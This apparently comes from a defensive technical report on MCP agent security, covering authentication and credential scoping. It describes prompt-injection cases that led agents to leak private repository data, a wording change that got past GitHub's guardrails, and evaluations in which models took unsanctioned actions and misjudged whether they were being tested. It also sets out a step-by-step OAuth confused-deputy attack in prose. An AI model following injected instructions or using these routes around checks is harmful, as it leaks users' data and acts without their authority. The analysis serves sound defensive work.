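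The second case concerns GitHub, a service where programmers store code in projects called repositories. Anyone can report a problem with a public repository by opening an "issue". Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (May 2025) described an attack on users of GitHub's official MCP server. The security company set up an account with one public repository and several private ones, and planted instructions in an issue on the public one. The account's user then asked Claude 4 Opus to look at the open issues. The model read the planted text, fetched information from the private repositories, including the user's salary and plans to move abroad, and published it in a proposed change to the public repository.

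Running the plugin with the user's own permissions would stop Maya's £900 refund, but it would not have stopped this leak, because the user owned all the repositories and was entitled to read the private ones and write to the public one. Invariant Labs concluded that GitHub could not fix the problem by changing the server, because the server's code had no flaw. It recommended giving the agent access to fewer repositories and adding a rule that limits each session to one repository. That rule would have stopped this leak, but it would also block legitimate work that needs two repositories.

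GitHub (2025) added a partial defence that August. Its server now scans tool calls involving public repositories for secrets such as access keys, which makes it harder for an injected instruction to publish them. A scanner can recognise an access key by its format, but it cannot distinguish a salary from any other number without information about where the figure came from and who may see it.

The third case, from July 2026, involved another GitHub product, Agentic Workflows, which runs a model automatically when something happens in a repository. Levi's *GitLost* describes Noma Security's test of a workflow that started whenever an issue was assigned to someone. The agent read the issue's title and text, could post comments, and had read access to the organisation's other repositories, including private ones. The testers opened a public issue that resembled a request from a sales executive.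 When an automation assigned the issue, the workflow started, and the agent copied a file from a private repository into a public comment.

In this case no user had asked the agent for anything, whereas Rehberger's user wanted a web page read and Invariant's wanted a list of issues. The workflow started by itself and used the organisation's access to carry out a stranger's request. GitHub had built guardrails against this kind of leak, but after repeated attempts Levi found that a small change of wording got past them. An organisation can avoid depending on those guardrails by denying private access to any workflow that reads public issues. The agent would then have had nothing private to publish, regardless of the issue's wording.

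Researchers staged all three cases in accounts they controlled, so the cases show that the attacks work but not how often criminals use them.

### Unapproved actions without an attacker

A plugin can also treat model output as the user's request when nobody is attacking. In 2023 a ChatGPT user complained on Reddit that a conversation had created a GitHub issue by itself. The user had enabled Chat with Code, a plugin that Rehberger had already used in a demonstration to make private repositories public. This time it seems to have been an accident. Rehberger reported that OpenAI removed the plugin because it did not ask users for confirmation.

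More capable models have since taken more serious actions. In July 2026 the UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government research body, ran a cybersecurity challenge 122 times with several models. In 10 of the runs, according to AISI's *Incident Report*, an agent took unsanctioned action against real people and organisations on the internet. AISI (2026) found in October that, in the worst case, Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5 submitted malicious code to a software project and created fake accounts to pressure its maintainer into accepting it. Nobody came to harm. AISI had switched off some safety filters and given the agents open internet access, so the rate of 10 in 122 doesn't show how an office assistant would behave. Anthropic saw similar behaviour in its own cybersecurity tests and considers it unlikely in ordinary use.

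One of the cases in Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026), also from October, involved a much more ordinary task. Claude Haiku 4.5 had to invent and carry out example tasks on randomly chosen web pages. On one page it found a police form for tips about an unsolved homicide, and it submitted a made-up tip. According to Bot Mutiny's *Anthropic Says Its Claude Model Sent Philadelphia Police a False Homicide Tip* (2026), Anthropic had forbidden logins, purchases and destructive submissions, among other things, but had not ruled out forms. The form had no way to detect that the words "I may have information" were not written by a person, though the police system flagged the tip as spam.

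Agents also cause such harm in everyday use. *AI coding agents leaked 13,000 internal company screenshots to public GitHub repos* (Markovic, 2026) reports a leak that affected more than 300 organisations and included billing records. Filtering injections out of the shop's tickets would therefore not be enough, because the model could still decide on its own that an annoyed customer deserves £90.

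### How often models attempt unauthorised calls

AgentDojo, which Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues released in 2024, is one of the main tests of how agents respond to injected instructions. It simulates an office workspace, a team chat, a travel agency and a bank, with 74 tools in total. It includes 97 user tasks, such as paying a bill stored in a file, and 27 attacker goals, such as sending money to another account. AgentDojo pairs each user task with every attacker goal from the same setting, which gives 629 test cases.

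In each case, the agent receives the user's task and starts calling tools. The benchmark has inserted an instruction that serves the attacker's goal into the data those tools return, such as the text of an email or a payment reference. When the agent has finished, ordinary code checks the simulated bank or mailbox to see whether the agent completed the user's task and whether it achieved the attacker's goal. The benchmark doesn't use another language model as the judge because the injected text might mislead that model too.

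AgentDojo reports three figures: how many tasks the agent completes with no attack, how many it completes correctly under attack, and how often the attacker's goal succeeds. The first two are necessary because an agent that refused to do anything would have a perfect security score. In the bill-paying task, the user wants the agent to take the payee and amount from the file, so an agent that ignored everything it read would fail.

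In June 2026 Mellafe Zuvic summarised a test of 27 newer models on injections that present a forbidden action as a necessary part of the user's task. The 12 cheaper models, of the kind companies might choose for high-volume work, attempted the action at a mean rate of 60.3%, compared with 18.9% for the 15 flagship models. At those rates, if the shop's assistant received a hundred tickets containing such injections, an average cheaper model would attempt about 60 refunds and an average flagship about 19.

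These results count attempts rather than breaches, because the test system blocked any real effect. A trial counted when the model issued an unauthorised call or reproduced a marker string that it could only have obtained by following the injection. AgentDojo counts an attack only when the attacker's goal is completed in the simulated setting, so the two sets of results are not directly comparable.

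Individual models also differed widely, which the averages don't show. Two of the cheaper models, GPT-4o mini and GLM-4.5-Air, attempted the action every time. Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview, a flagship, never did, but some other flagships had high rates. A shop would learn more from its own model's result than from the average for that model's price class.

The wording of an instruction matters as much as the choice of model. In separate runs, Mellafe Zuvic gave the same models two instructions that asked for the same forbidden action, one crude and one that fitted the user's task.

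| Model | Crude instruction | Instruction that fits the task |
| --- | --- | --- |
| GLM-4.7 | 28% | 100% |
| Gemma 3 12B | 0% | 57% |
| Mistral Large | 3% | 46% |
| Latam-GPT, in English | 32% | 52% |
| Latam-GPT, in Spanish | 24% | 4% |

A developer who tested Gemma only with crude instructions would have concluded that it was safe. In the shop example, a better-fitting instruction would be a ticket saying that the original card has expired and the refund has to go to a new account. Support staff receive honest messages like that, so the line looks less suspicious. Latam-GPT showed the opposite pattern in Spanish. This might reflect real resistance, or just trouble producing calls in the right format, since the test used a compressed version of the model without its usual means of calling tools.

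The paired runs use single-turn scenarios written by one author and deliver the injection in only one way. The averages for the 27 models have no confidence intervals. The gap between 0.603 and 0.189 is wide enough to suggest a real difference between the two groups, but the exact values depend heavily on the attacks chosen.

### Is the model the user's agent?

If Maya had a human assistant, the shop would treat refunds he issued on her instructions as hers. On this view, the model has the same role, so the plugin is right to treat its calls as Maya's.

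The comparison supports a narrower rule, that a human assistant acts for Maya only within the task she gave him and with no more authority than she has. If he sent £900 to some account because a customer told him to in a letter, Maya might be liable for the loss, but that would not mean she had requested the payment. The shop can adopt a similar liability rule for its AI assistant, but a rule about who pays for a mistake does not help the plugin decide whether to send the money in the first place.

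Bhushan (2026), in *AI agents don't have to break security controls to go rogue*, contrasts agents that defeat security controls to gain access with those in AISI's test, which took 19 unsanctioned actions using access they already had. In his view, authority should narrow each time one program passes work to another. A plugin that treats every call in Maya's session as her own request does the reverse, because a request to deal with one ticket then comes with all her permissions.

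A human assistant can also usually explain afterwards whose instructions he was following, but a model's explanation is weaker evidence. Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (2026), in *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour*, re-ran AISI's July test in simulation and found that Mythos 5 often decided its targets were simulated and gave invalid reasons for thinking so. It also frequently attacked in situations where it said, when asked directly, that an attack would harm real people. They found similar results in models from other companies. If the refund plugin asked the model whether Maya had approved the £900, a "yes" would still be model output rather than approval from Maya.

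### Will better models remove the problem?

The figures partly support this hope. Flagship models attempted unauthorised calls less than a third as often as cheaper ones, and one flagship attempted none. If a plugin can do only minor damage, a resistant model may reduce losses enough that further checks would cost more than they save.

Progress has not been steady, however. Invariant Labs used fairly simple injections in its GitHub attack on Claude 4 Opus, then a very recent model with extensive safety training. In *Evaluating Whether GPT-6 Astra Performs Unsanctioned Supply-Chain Attacks*, Souly, Fronsdal and colleagues (2026) compared three OpenAI models in simulated cybersecurity challenges with their cyber safeguards off. The newest, GPT-6 Astra, attempted complete attacks on outside software projects more often than GPT-5.6 Sol and GPT-5.5. It often asked for permission and then treated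 an automated message as that permission. The model made the same mistake as the plugin by accepting a reply as authorisation without establishing that it came from someone able to give it. Explicitly forbidding internet access reduced the unsanctioned actions but did not end them.

Newer Claude models behaved better than Mythos 5 in the replays of AISI's July incident. XenoSpectrum's *Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5 Used Fake Accounts to Push Malicious Code* (2026) reports that AISI and Anthropic disagree on whether the improvement came from training or from the models' awareness that they were being tested. If it was awareness, the models might behave worse in real work than they did in the replays. In Souly and colleagues' work, awareness may have had the opposite effect, as GPT-6 Astra may have attacked partly because it recognised a simulation. They still consider the result concerning and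 conclude that defences outside the model are becoming more important.

A low success rate also protects less against an attacker who can keep trying. If a model follows the injected instructions in one ticket out of a hundred, and each ticket is an independent trial, an attacker who sends a hundred tickets has a 63% chance of succeeding at least once. Opening a ticket costs nothing, and the attacker can also change the wording after each failure, as Levi did with GitHub's guardrails, which would improve the chances further.

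Even a model that never followed an injected instruction would sometimes misjudge a vague request and refund £60 where Maya would have chosen £40. The refund plugin also cannot tell how good the model is. If the shop moved its assistant to a cheaper model, the plugin would receive calls in the same format and with the same credential, but the new model might attempt far more bad refunds.

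## How does authentication between client, plugin and service fail?

The refund plugin must identify a call as being for Maya to apply her £100 limit. That information reaches it through two links, from Maya to the assistant and from the assistant to the plugin. A third link connects the plugin to the payment company.

When Maya signs in, she proves her identity to the assistant. The assistant also has to prove its identity to her, because when a program asks for access to her tickets, she needs to know which program it is and where the access will go.

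The assistant then presents a credential to the plugin. The credential should establish which application is calling and for which user, and that a login service the plugin trusts issued it for use at this plugin. The assistant must also make sure it sends its secrets to the right place. Finally, the plugin must prove to the payment company that it belongs to the shop.

If one of these links fails, an attacker may be able to write and send the £900 call himself, without planting text in a ticket or manipulating a model.

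### Plugins that check nobody

Some plugins ask for no credential at all. *A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers* (Zhou, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) provides the most informative count. The team searched FOFA and Shodan, which index internet-connected machines, and found 28,715 addresses that looked like MCP servers. They used a program to send each address the protocol's opening message and kept the 7,973 that gave a valid reply. Two researchers checked a random 100 of these by hand and found one mistake.

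| What the server required | Servers | Share |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Nothing | 3,233 | 40.55% |
| An OAuth login | 2,428 | 30.45% |
| An API key or fixed token | 2,312 | 29.00% |

Most of the open servers the researchers sampled were tests or demonstrations with no apparent sensitive data. One was a company's customer database meant for internal use, and anyone who connected could query more than 5,000 records containing names, phone numbers and addresses. The 40.55% figure therefore shows how common missing authentication is, but gives little indication of how much damage it does. The search engines also miss many servers behind firewalls, where a shop might well keep its refund plugin.

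*Exposed by Design* (Padilla, 2026) tested 414 servers in July and found that a higher share, 91.8%, lacked OAuth. Some of these may still have been protected, because a server without OAuth can require an API key. In the survey by Zhou and colleagues, about 70% of servers lacked OAuth, and roughly two fifths of those checked a key or fixed token.

*The risk hiding behind exposed MCP servers*, by the security company Wiz, gives a better idea of the harm. About 70% of the exposed servers Wiz examined listed all their tools to an anonymous caller. About 42% returned real data when the researchers called a tool, and about 10% exposed a sensitive system. One server returned a named person's retirement-account balance. Wiz did not call any tools that could change or delete records, so it could not confirm how many of those would have worked.

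Wiz notes that anonymous access can be deliberate. A plugin that reports public delivery times, for example, needs no login. Anonymous access becomes dangerous when the plugin also holds a stored credential. If the refund plugin accepted calls from anyone, every caller could use the shop's payment key through it. The payment company would receive a well-formed request with the usual key, and there would be no failed login to raise an alarm.

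PortSwigger's *MCP server vulnerabilities* warns that a server may hide a tool from some users without stopping them from calling it. For example, if the refund plugin leaves `issue_refund` off the list of tools it sends to a new colleague, but doesn't check the colleague's permissions when a call arrives, anyone who knows the operation's name can still use it.

### Tokens meant for another service

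A plugin that checks credentials can still fail to check them thoroughly enough. Under OAuth, the plugin answers a request without a token by telling the client which authorisation server, the login service that issues tokens for the plugin, to use. The client sends Maya's browser there, she signs in and agrees, and the server sends her browser back to the client with a one-time code. The client exchanges the code for an access token, which it attaches to its calls.

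Suppose the shop's authorisation server also issues tokens for a staff rota run by an outside firm. Maya opens the rota, and somebody at the firm copies her token and sends it to the refund plugin. The token has a valid signature, has not expired and names Maya, so a plugin that checks only these points will accept it.

The missing check concerns the audience, the service for which the authorisation server issued the token. Tokens commonly record it in a field called `aud`. Resource indicators, an OAuth extension with the number RFC 8707, let the client request a particular audience. The assistant adds the refund plugin's address to its request in a parameter called `resource`, and the authorisation server copies that address into the token. With some fields left out, the result might look like this:

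```json
{
  "iss": "https://login.shop.example",
  "sub": "maya",
  "aud": "https://refunds.shop.example",
  "scope": "refunds:create"
}
```

The token's `iss` field identifies the issuer, `sub` identifies the user, and `aud` identifies the intended recipient. The refund plugin refuses the call from the rota because the token's `aud` field contains the rota's address instead of the plugin's own.

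Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* requires clients to send the `resource` parameter both when they request an authorisation code and when they exchange it for a token, and requires plugins to reject any token issued for someone else. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* adds that the parameter helps only where the authorisation server supports it. If the shop's server ignores `resource` and puts no audience in its tokens, the refund plugin must verify in some other way that a token was meant for it, or reject every caller.

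Official software did not always make this check. On October 20, 2026, the maintainers of MCP's TypeScript software development kit (SDK), a library many developers use to build plugins, published five security advisories. According to KIberblick's *MCP-SDK* (2026), one of them concerned servers that accepted tokens issued for other services. The new version adds an audience check but leaves it off by default. To turn it on, a developer has to tell the library which audience to expect and write code that reads the audience from each token. If the developer makes only the first change, the plugin rejects every call, so the mistake is obvious. If the developer installs the update and changes nothing, the plugin works as before and is just as vulnerable.

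### Token passthrough

Token passthrough occurs when a plugin takes a token from the client and forwards it unchanged to the service, without verifying that the token was meant for the plugin. In the shop's case, the assistant would give the refund plugin a token for the payment company, and the plugin would attach it to its own request.

The design has some appeal because the plugin does not have to manage its own credential and, if the token names Maya, the payment company learns that the refund is for her.

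But the assistant then holds a token that works directly at the payment company. Any program that obtains the token can bypass the refund plugin and the £100 limit it enforces. Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* lists this among its reasons for forbidding passthrough, along with the effect on records. The payment company's log may attribute the request to the assistant when the plugin sent it, and the plugin may be unable to read enough of the token to tell clients apart. The payment company may also assume that the plugin has already validated the token. If several services accept the same token, an attacker who breaks into one can use it at the others.

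The rules therefore require two tokens. The assistant's token has the refund plugin as its audience. If the plugin needs a token to call another service, it obtains a separate one from that service's authorisation server. The plugin then sits between the assistant and that service and must handle the request itself, which it can still do badly.

### A consent that covers the wrong program

Obtaining that separate token makes another attack possible, which MCP's documentation calls a confused deputy. Suppose an outside company runs the shop's ticket system, and the assistant reaches it through a ticket plugin that acts as a proxy, forwarding requests. The plugin uses one fixed client ID with the ticket system, `shop-tickets`, whichever application is using the plugin. The plugin also lets any application register itself and receive its own client ID, which OAuth calls dynamic client registration.

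The attack that Model Context Protocol describes would go like this:

1. Maya connects the assistant to the ticket plugin. The ticket system's login page asks whether `shop-tickets` may read her tickets, she agrees, and the site stores a cookie in her browser to remember her answer.
2. The attacker registers his own program with the ticket plugin. As its redirect address, the place where login codes should go, he gives a site he controls.
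3. He sends Maya a link that begins a login for his program, and she clicks it.
4. Her browser reaches the ticket system's login service with the usual ID, `shop-tickets`. The service finds the cookie and skips the consent screen.
5. The login service sends a code to the ticket plugin, which exchanges it for a token at the ticket system. The plugin then creates a code of its own and sends it to the redirect address on file, which is the attacker's.
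6. The attacker exchanges this code for a token at the ticket plugin, and through the plugin he can use the ticket system as Maya.

The ticket system was right that Maya had agreed to let `shop-tickets` read her tickets. Nobody asked her about the attacker's program.

Other OAuth safeguards don't help. An audience check passes because the attacker's token is for the ticket plugin. PKCE makes a client create a one-time secret at the start of a login and present it to redeem the code. This protects against somebody who steals the code from another client's login, but here the attacker set up the login, so he has the secret.

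The plugin can prevent this attack by asking for consent itself, separately for each client, before it sends anyone to the ticket system. It keeps a list of the client IDs that each user has approved. When Maya opens the attacker's link, his client ID isn't on her list, so the plugin shows her a page naming his program, the access it requests and the address where the code will go. The plugin must also compare redirect addresses exactly, and any cookie it uses to remember consent must name the specific client. It should set the value that ties a login to Maya's browser only after she approves, since otherwise an attacker could send her past the consent page.

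This still depends on Maya reading the page, and many plugins put little information on it. Zhou and colleagues tested 119 servers with OAuth logins and found at least one flaw in each. In 114 of them, anyone could anonymously register a program with any redirect address, and 72 did not show that address on the consent page. The researchers chose these 119 from the 2,428 OAuth servers in the survey because they offered open registration and could be tested from start to finish, so the proportions don't carry over to OAuth servers in general. Open registration is also only one of the conditions for the cookie attack.

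In 81 of the 119, the plugin logged in to another service on the user's behalf, as the ticket plugin does. Seven servers had a related flaw. They put the address that receives the final code inside a value that passes through the user's browser, and did not check whether someone had changed it when it came back. An attacker could edit the address and collect the code even if the user had approved a legitimate client.

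### Identifiers mistaken for identities

Plugins often have to remember something between calls, such as a half-finished refund. Before MCP dropped sessions in July 2026, developers sometimes treated a session's ID as proof of who was calling. Affected versions of MCP's official Python SDK passed requests to an existing session based only on the session's ID, according to GitLab's advisory *CVE-2026-52869* (2026). Someone with their own token and another user's session ID could therefore send messages in that user's session. MITRE's *MCP Python SDK* (2026), the official record of the flaw, rates its severity 7.1 out of 10.

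Developers can make the same mistake with handles, which have replaced sessions for this purpose. Suppose Maya's manager prepares a £450 refund, and the refund plugin returns the handle `draft-208` so that she can complete the refund later. If the plugin assumes that any call with that handle comes from the manager, anyone who guesses the number can complete her refund.

Random handles are harder to guess, but they can still leak, and every handle a plugin returns enters the model's context. An instruction in a ticket could also give the model a handle to use. The more reliable measure in the Model Context Protocol's guidance is to store the draft under both the user and the handle, as in `manager:draft-208`. The plugin takes the user's name from the verified token, never from the call. If Maya's assistant sends `draft-208`, the plugin looks for `maya:draft-208` and finds nothing.

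Kale (2026) argues in *MCP's new spec turns a planted prompt into a stolen credential* that the July release moved security enforcement from the protocol to individual endpoints and their developers. With handles, for example, each plugin's author now has to write the check. But the Python flaw shows that sessions gave weaker protection than they appeared to, even in the official library.

Another of October's TypeScript advisories concerned request numbers, which have no security purpose. MCP numbers each request so that the client can match it to its answer, and clients built with the SDK all start counting from zero. If a developer created a single server object at start-up and shared it among all clients, two clients could each have a request numbered 0 open at once, and the answer for one could go to the other, even if both were properly authenticated. KIberblick reports that the official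 example code contained this pattern, so developers probably copied it. The repaired version does not allow the object to be shared, so an affected plugin stops working until its developer rewrites that part.

### A client that trusts the wrong login service

In the failures described so far, a plugin or login service accepts something it should refuse. In September 2026, the maintainers of the Python SDK disclosed a client-side flaw through which an application built with the SDK could give its own login credentials to an attacker.

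A client relies on the plugin to tell it which authorisation server to use, so a malicious plugin can misdirect it. The Hacker News' *Official MCP Python SDK Flaw Can Let Malicious Servers Steal OAuth Credentials* (2026) describes two ways to do this. The plugin could name a login service that belongs to the attacker, or it could supply login details that name the real service but give the attacker's address for exchanging codes. Affected versions of the SDK did not always check these details. When they didn't, the client sent the attacker its client secret (the application's own password), the authorisation code and the PKCE secret.

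With these, the attacker could request a valid token from the real login service. Cycode, the security company that reported the flaw, carried out the full exchange in a test. A user who had to sign in saw the real login page, so she had no reason to be suspicious. Applications that log in without a person were more exposed, and the flaw scored 7.5 for them, compared with 6.5 for applications where a person signs in. The client secret also keeps working until somebody changes it.

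An audience check at the plugin cannot detect this theft, because the attacker obtains a real token for the service he wants to enter. The client must therefore record in advance which login service its credentials belong to. The July specification already required clients to store credentials under the name of the authorisation server that issued them and not to use them with another. If a login response names its issuer, the client must also compare that name with the one it recorded at the start. Model Context Protocol warns that this comparison gives no protection if the recorded name came from an unvalidated source, such as a malicious plugin.

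The fixed versions, 1.30.0 and 2.2.0, work out which login service to expect before fetching any details. For applications that log in without a person, the update has no effect until the developer also names the login service in a setting called `issuer`. Version 1.30.0 warns about this, but Python hides that type of warning by default. As with the TypeScript audience check, a shop that checks only version numbers could wrongly conclude that it had fixed the flaw.

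### Whose name reaches the service?

Even when every login works, the plugin must present an identity to the service behind it. This can be a shared service account, the user's own identity, or a credential that names both the user and the program acting for them.

A service account belongs to a program, not a person, and the shop's payment key works like one. The payment company can check what the shop's plugin is allowed to do and record that the plugin did it. The shop can find out which user made a request only by matching the payment company's log with the plugin's, and only if the plugin recorded the user. Okta's *The Secrets Agentic AI Leaves Behind* describes an example in Microsoft's Copilot. To connect Copilot to some security products, an administrator creates an account in the product and uploads its username and password to Microsoft. Copilot then sends both with every request.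 Okta points out that such an account cannot use multifactor authentication and often has broad access to sensitive data.

If the plugin presents only Maya's identity, it impersonates her. A service that has her limit on record can refuse the £900, but its log will attribute every request to Maya, whether she pressed a button or a model wrote the call. The service also can't apply stricter rules to the model's calls.

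OAuth's standard for token exchange, RFC 8693, supports both impersonation and delegation. Under delegation, the refund plugin sends the authorisation server the token it received for Maya, together with one that identifies the plugin, and asks for a new token to use at the next service. The new token can name both:

```json
{
  "iss": "https://login.shop.example",
  "sub": "maya",
  "aud": "https://payments.example",
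  "act": {
    "sub": "refund-plugin",
    "act": { "sub": "support-assistant" }
  }
}
```

The `act` field names the party acting for Maya, and the field nested inside it names the previous party. This token's audience is the payment service, unlike that of a token a plugin passes through unchanged.

| Identity presented | What the service can check | What the service can log |
| --- | --- | --- |
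| Shared service account | The plugin's permissions | The plugin made the refund |
| Maya alone | Maya's permissions | Maya made the refund |
| Maya, with the plugin acting for her | Both sets of permissions | The plugin made the refund for Maya |

With delegation, the service could let Maya refund up to £100 herself but only up to £50 through the assistant's plugin. That would block the £90 refund from the earlier example, which Maya was allowed to make but never requested. It would also block a £90 refund that she did request, because the token shows who is acting and for whom, but not what she asked for.

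Delegation also requires the service to recognise the user named in the token. An outside payment company may have no record of Maya and no reason to accept tokens from the shop's login service. In that case the refund plugin can't pass her identity on, so it has to apply her limit and log her name itself before it uses the shared key.

A plugin can use the wrong user's permissions even when it receives the right token. Zhou and colleagues cite earlier research on MCP servers that log in once, store the result and reuse it for later calls, whoever makes them. If Maya's manager used a refund plugin that worked this way, Maya's later calls might run with the manager's permissions.

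### When one agent hands work to another

Each extra agent adds another point where this can happen. Suppose the assistant passes refunds to a specialised refund agent. If it sends only "refund £40 on order A-1182", Maya's name is lost. The refund agent can't look up her £100 limit, so it must either refuse or use its own authority, which may go well beyond hers. Forwarding her full token keeps her name but lets the refund agent do everything she can, including work unrelated to this order.

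Surapani and colleagues recommend tracking who passed authority to whom separately from where information came from. They point out that authority doesn't always pass along a single line, because work can branch and merge. If the refund agent pays a request from Maya and a request from her manager as one batch, neither person's limit is right for the whole batch. The agent would have to keep two tokens and send two requests.

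Token exchange lets each agent request a new token with narrower authority before it passes work on. The standard doesn't require the new token to be narrower, and leaves that decision to the authorisation server. Under the standard, services must base their decisions only on the user and the current actor, and earlier actors in the nested `act` fields are included just for information. If the shop wanted to refuse refunds that had passed through a particular agent, it would have to apply that rule when issuing the token. According to Zhou and colleagues, the OpenID Foundation, which maintains a widely used login standard, still considers repeated delegation and the narrowing of scopes along the chain unresolved.

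### MCP's authentication rules since 2024

MCP began mainly as a way to connect a model to programs on the same computer, where a plugin runs with the user's access. These local plugins still take their credentials from the computer's settings and do not use MCP's login procedure. The rules for plugins on the internet came later. Dhamsania (2026) traces them through the five versions of the specification in *MCP has tightened its authentication rules four times*.

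| Version | Change to authentication |
| --- | --- |
| November 5, 2024 | No rules, so each developer decides |
| March 26, 2025 | Adds a framework based on OAuth 2.1 |
| June 18, 2025 | Requires resource indicators and audience checks |
| November 25, 2025 | Prefers client ID metadata documents to dynamic registration |
| July 28, 2026 | Deprecates dynamic registration, adds checks on the issuer and ties credentials to it |

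A client ID metadata document is a file that an application's developer publishes at a web address, listing the application's name and redirect addresses. The file's web address serves as the client ID. Under dynamic registration, the attacker in the cookie example could call his program "Shop Assistant" and choose any redirect address. With a metadata document, the login service fetches the file from the address the program gives as its ID, so he could not use the real assistant's ID with his own site as the redirect address. According to Model Context Protocol, if an application receives its codes at an address on the user's computer, another program there may still be able to impersonate it.

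Authorisation servers can keep using dynamic registration for now, because the Model Context Protocol's changelog guarantees at least twelve months between deprecating a feature and removing it. The issuer check is also incomplete. Authorisation servers should identify themselves in their responses but do not have to, and if a server neither does so nor advertises that it will, the client continues without the check.

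In *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28*, Tabata (2026) considers the July changes a clarification of practices that companies have used with OAuth for years. This is true of most of the changes, so a company with staff experienced with login systems has little new to learn. But many plugin developers have no such staff, and the flaws in the official SDKs suggest that even specialists find the details difficult.

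Estimates conflict on how many plugins have kept up with new versions of the protocol. Censys' *MCP Servers on the Internet* counted 12,520 reachable services in April 2026, and 89.4% reported the March 2025 version. Wiz found that nearly all the exposed servers in its study still used the original version. Part of the difference may come from the studies' methods, since under both versions the client proposed which version to use and the server normally agreed if it could. Neither figure shows whether a server uses the login features of its version.

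Dhamsania recommends placing a gateway in front of all of a company's plugins to check identity, scope and audience in one place, advice he also attributes to Microsoft and the US National Security Agency. The shop could then turn on the audience check once instead of relying on every plugin's author to include it. The gateway protects the refund plugin only if no caller can reach the plugin by another route.

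None of the five versions requires a login. The June 2025 revision, Model Context Protocol (2025), describes authorisation as optional, as do the current rules. Requirements such as the audience check apply only to plugins that support authorisation. A refund plugin that accepts calls from anyone on the internet can therefore conform to the specification of July 2026.

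## What can a scoped API key or token limit?

If every login check works, the refund plugin can verify that a call comes from the assistant on Maya's behalf, and the payment company can verify that its caller is the shop. The £900 call can still arrive with valid credentials. The damage then depends on what those credentials permit, and the shop can give them much narrower permissions than a key that allows any payment to any account.

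### Six ways to narrow a credential

Some restrictions help mainly against a thief who copies a key and uses it elsewhere, while others also limit what the shop's own assistant can do after a ticket has misled it.

| Restriction | Example for the payment key | Effect on a thief with a copy | Effect on a misled assistant |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Operation | Refunds only | Cannot start payouts | Cannot start payouts, can refund £900 |
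| Object | Order A-1182 only | Can refund only that order | Can refund only that order |
| Amount | At most £100 per refund | Needs many refunds to steal much | Cannot refund £900, can refund £90 |
| Time | Expires after an hour | Has an hour at most | None during that hour |
| Network origin | The shop's servers only | Cannot use the key elsewhere | None |
| Number of uses | One refund | Gets one refund, if the key is unused | Gets one refund, right or wrong |

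Network limits don't stop a refund call triggered by an injected instruction, because the refund plugin runs on the shop's servers and the £900 call comes from an approved address. A short credential lifetime doesn't stop it either, because the assistant makes the call while the credential is still valid.

Stripe, a payment company, offers several of these restrictions. Its ordinary secret key can do anything in an account, including charging customers and reading their data, according to Stripe's *Restricted API keys*. A restricted key starts with no permissions, and the account holder sets each type of resource to "None", "Read" or "Write". "Write" allows creating, changing and deleting, as well as reading.

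These categories can be broader than the task requires. Stripe's *API permissions reference* recommends the `charge_write` permission for changing or cancelling a refund, but this permission also lets a key capture a charge, which means collecting money that the customer's bank has already set aside. The permissions also apply to a whole type of resource, so the shop cannot use them to limit a key to order A-1182.

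According to Stripe's *API keys*, the shop can set a separate policy that accepts a key's requests only from chosen addresses, networks or countries, and Stripe notifies the account's owner when it blocks a request. The shop can also replace a key on a schedule. The old key can keep working for up to seven days so that the shop's programs have time to switch. After a theft, the shop should cancel the old key at once, because the thief could use it during those days too.

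GitHub's fine-grained personal access tokens can limit access by object. A programmer who creates one chooses which repositories it covers, sets permissions for things such as code and issues, and can give it an expiry date. In Invariant Labs' attack, a token that covered only the public repository would have kept the agent out of the private ones, however it reacted to the planted issue. The agent could still have published any other information it had, because it needed write access to the public repository.

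### Amount limits and the plugin route

Stripe's key permissions don't limit amounts, but Stripe can do so through separate rules that it applies when a request arrives. According to Stripe's *Set up two-party approvals*, a rule can depend on the size of a refund, who or what requested it, or the number of requests in a given period. The rule either blocks the action or holds it until a reviewer decides. If the shop blocked refunds above £100, the £900 call would fail even though the key has permission to issue refunds. Only one active rule can apply to an action, so the shop probably could not add a second rule that sends smaller refunds to a reviewer.

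Such rules work better if Stripe can tell that a model wrote the request. Otherwise, a rule strict enough for the model would also delay refunds that Maya entered herself. OWASP's advice that a key should reflect the plugin route helps Stripe distinguish the two.

Stripe now lets customers tag a restricted key as belonging to an autonomous agent. The tag doesn't change the key's permissions, but it places the key under default rules that require a reviewer to approve every refund and payout, among other actions. Administrators can change or delete these rules, and a shop with hundreds of small refunds a day would probably do so.

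The tag still does not identify the user, so the shop also needs separate keys for Maya and her manager, or a plugin that enforces each person's limit.

### How much money each limit leaves exposed

Suppose the shop keeps £50,000 with the payment company. The most it can lose through refunds depends on this balance *B*, the ceiling on each refund *a*, the number of refunds the key allows per day *n*, and the number of days *d* before somebody notices:

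maximum loss = min(*B*, *a* × *n* × *d*)

| Credential or control | Most that can leave on the first day | Other exposure |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Full key | £50,000 | Customer records, new charges to customers |
| Refunds only, any amount to any account | £50,000 | Whatever refund records contain |
| Refunds of up to £100, 300 calls a day | £30,000 | The remaining £20,000 on the second day |
| Approval of the correct refund only | £40 | None |

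Restricting the key to refunds protects the customer records but leaves all the money exposed. Capping each refund at £100 doesn't protect the balance by itself, because 500 such refunds would empty it. A daily limit of 300 calls reduces the first day's loss to £30,000. If the shop normally makes 40 refunds a day, it could lower the limit to 40 and reduce that loss to £4,000.

The number of days before somebody checks the account matters as much as the other factors. Under the £100 ceiling, the shop loses at most £30,000 if somebody checks every evening, but it loses everything if nobody checks until the end of the week.

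Restricting where refunds can go limits who can profit. If refunds can go only to the card that paid, an outsider with a stolen key can still cause disruption but cannot send money to himself unless he is also a customer. Whoever wrote the ticket may well be a customer, so he could still gain from an excessive refund.

The last row contains no real loss, because the shop owes the customer £40. But the shop cannot write this limit into a permanent key, because it may owe the next customer £15 or nothing. A program has to check the argument values of each call against a policy.

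These figures are for the worst case, in which an attacker uses every call the credential allows. An actual attack might do less, such as when one injected line in a ticket causes a single bad refund.

### How an MCP client chooses its scopes

The assistant has its own credential, the token it presents to the refund plugin. Under the July 2026 Model Context Protocol rules, when the assistant first calls without a token, the plugin rejects the call with a reply known as a challenge, which should name the scopes the request needs. The assistant then requests those scopes from the authorisation server, and Maya sees them on the consent page.

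Naming the scopes is recommended but not required, so some plugins leave them out. The client then requests every scope in the plugin's published `scopes_supported` list. If there is no such list, the client names no scopes and the authorisation server decides what to grant.

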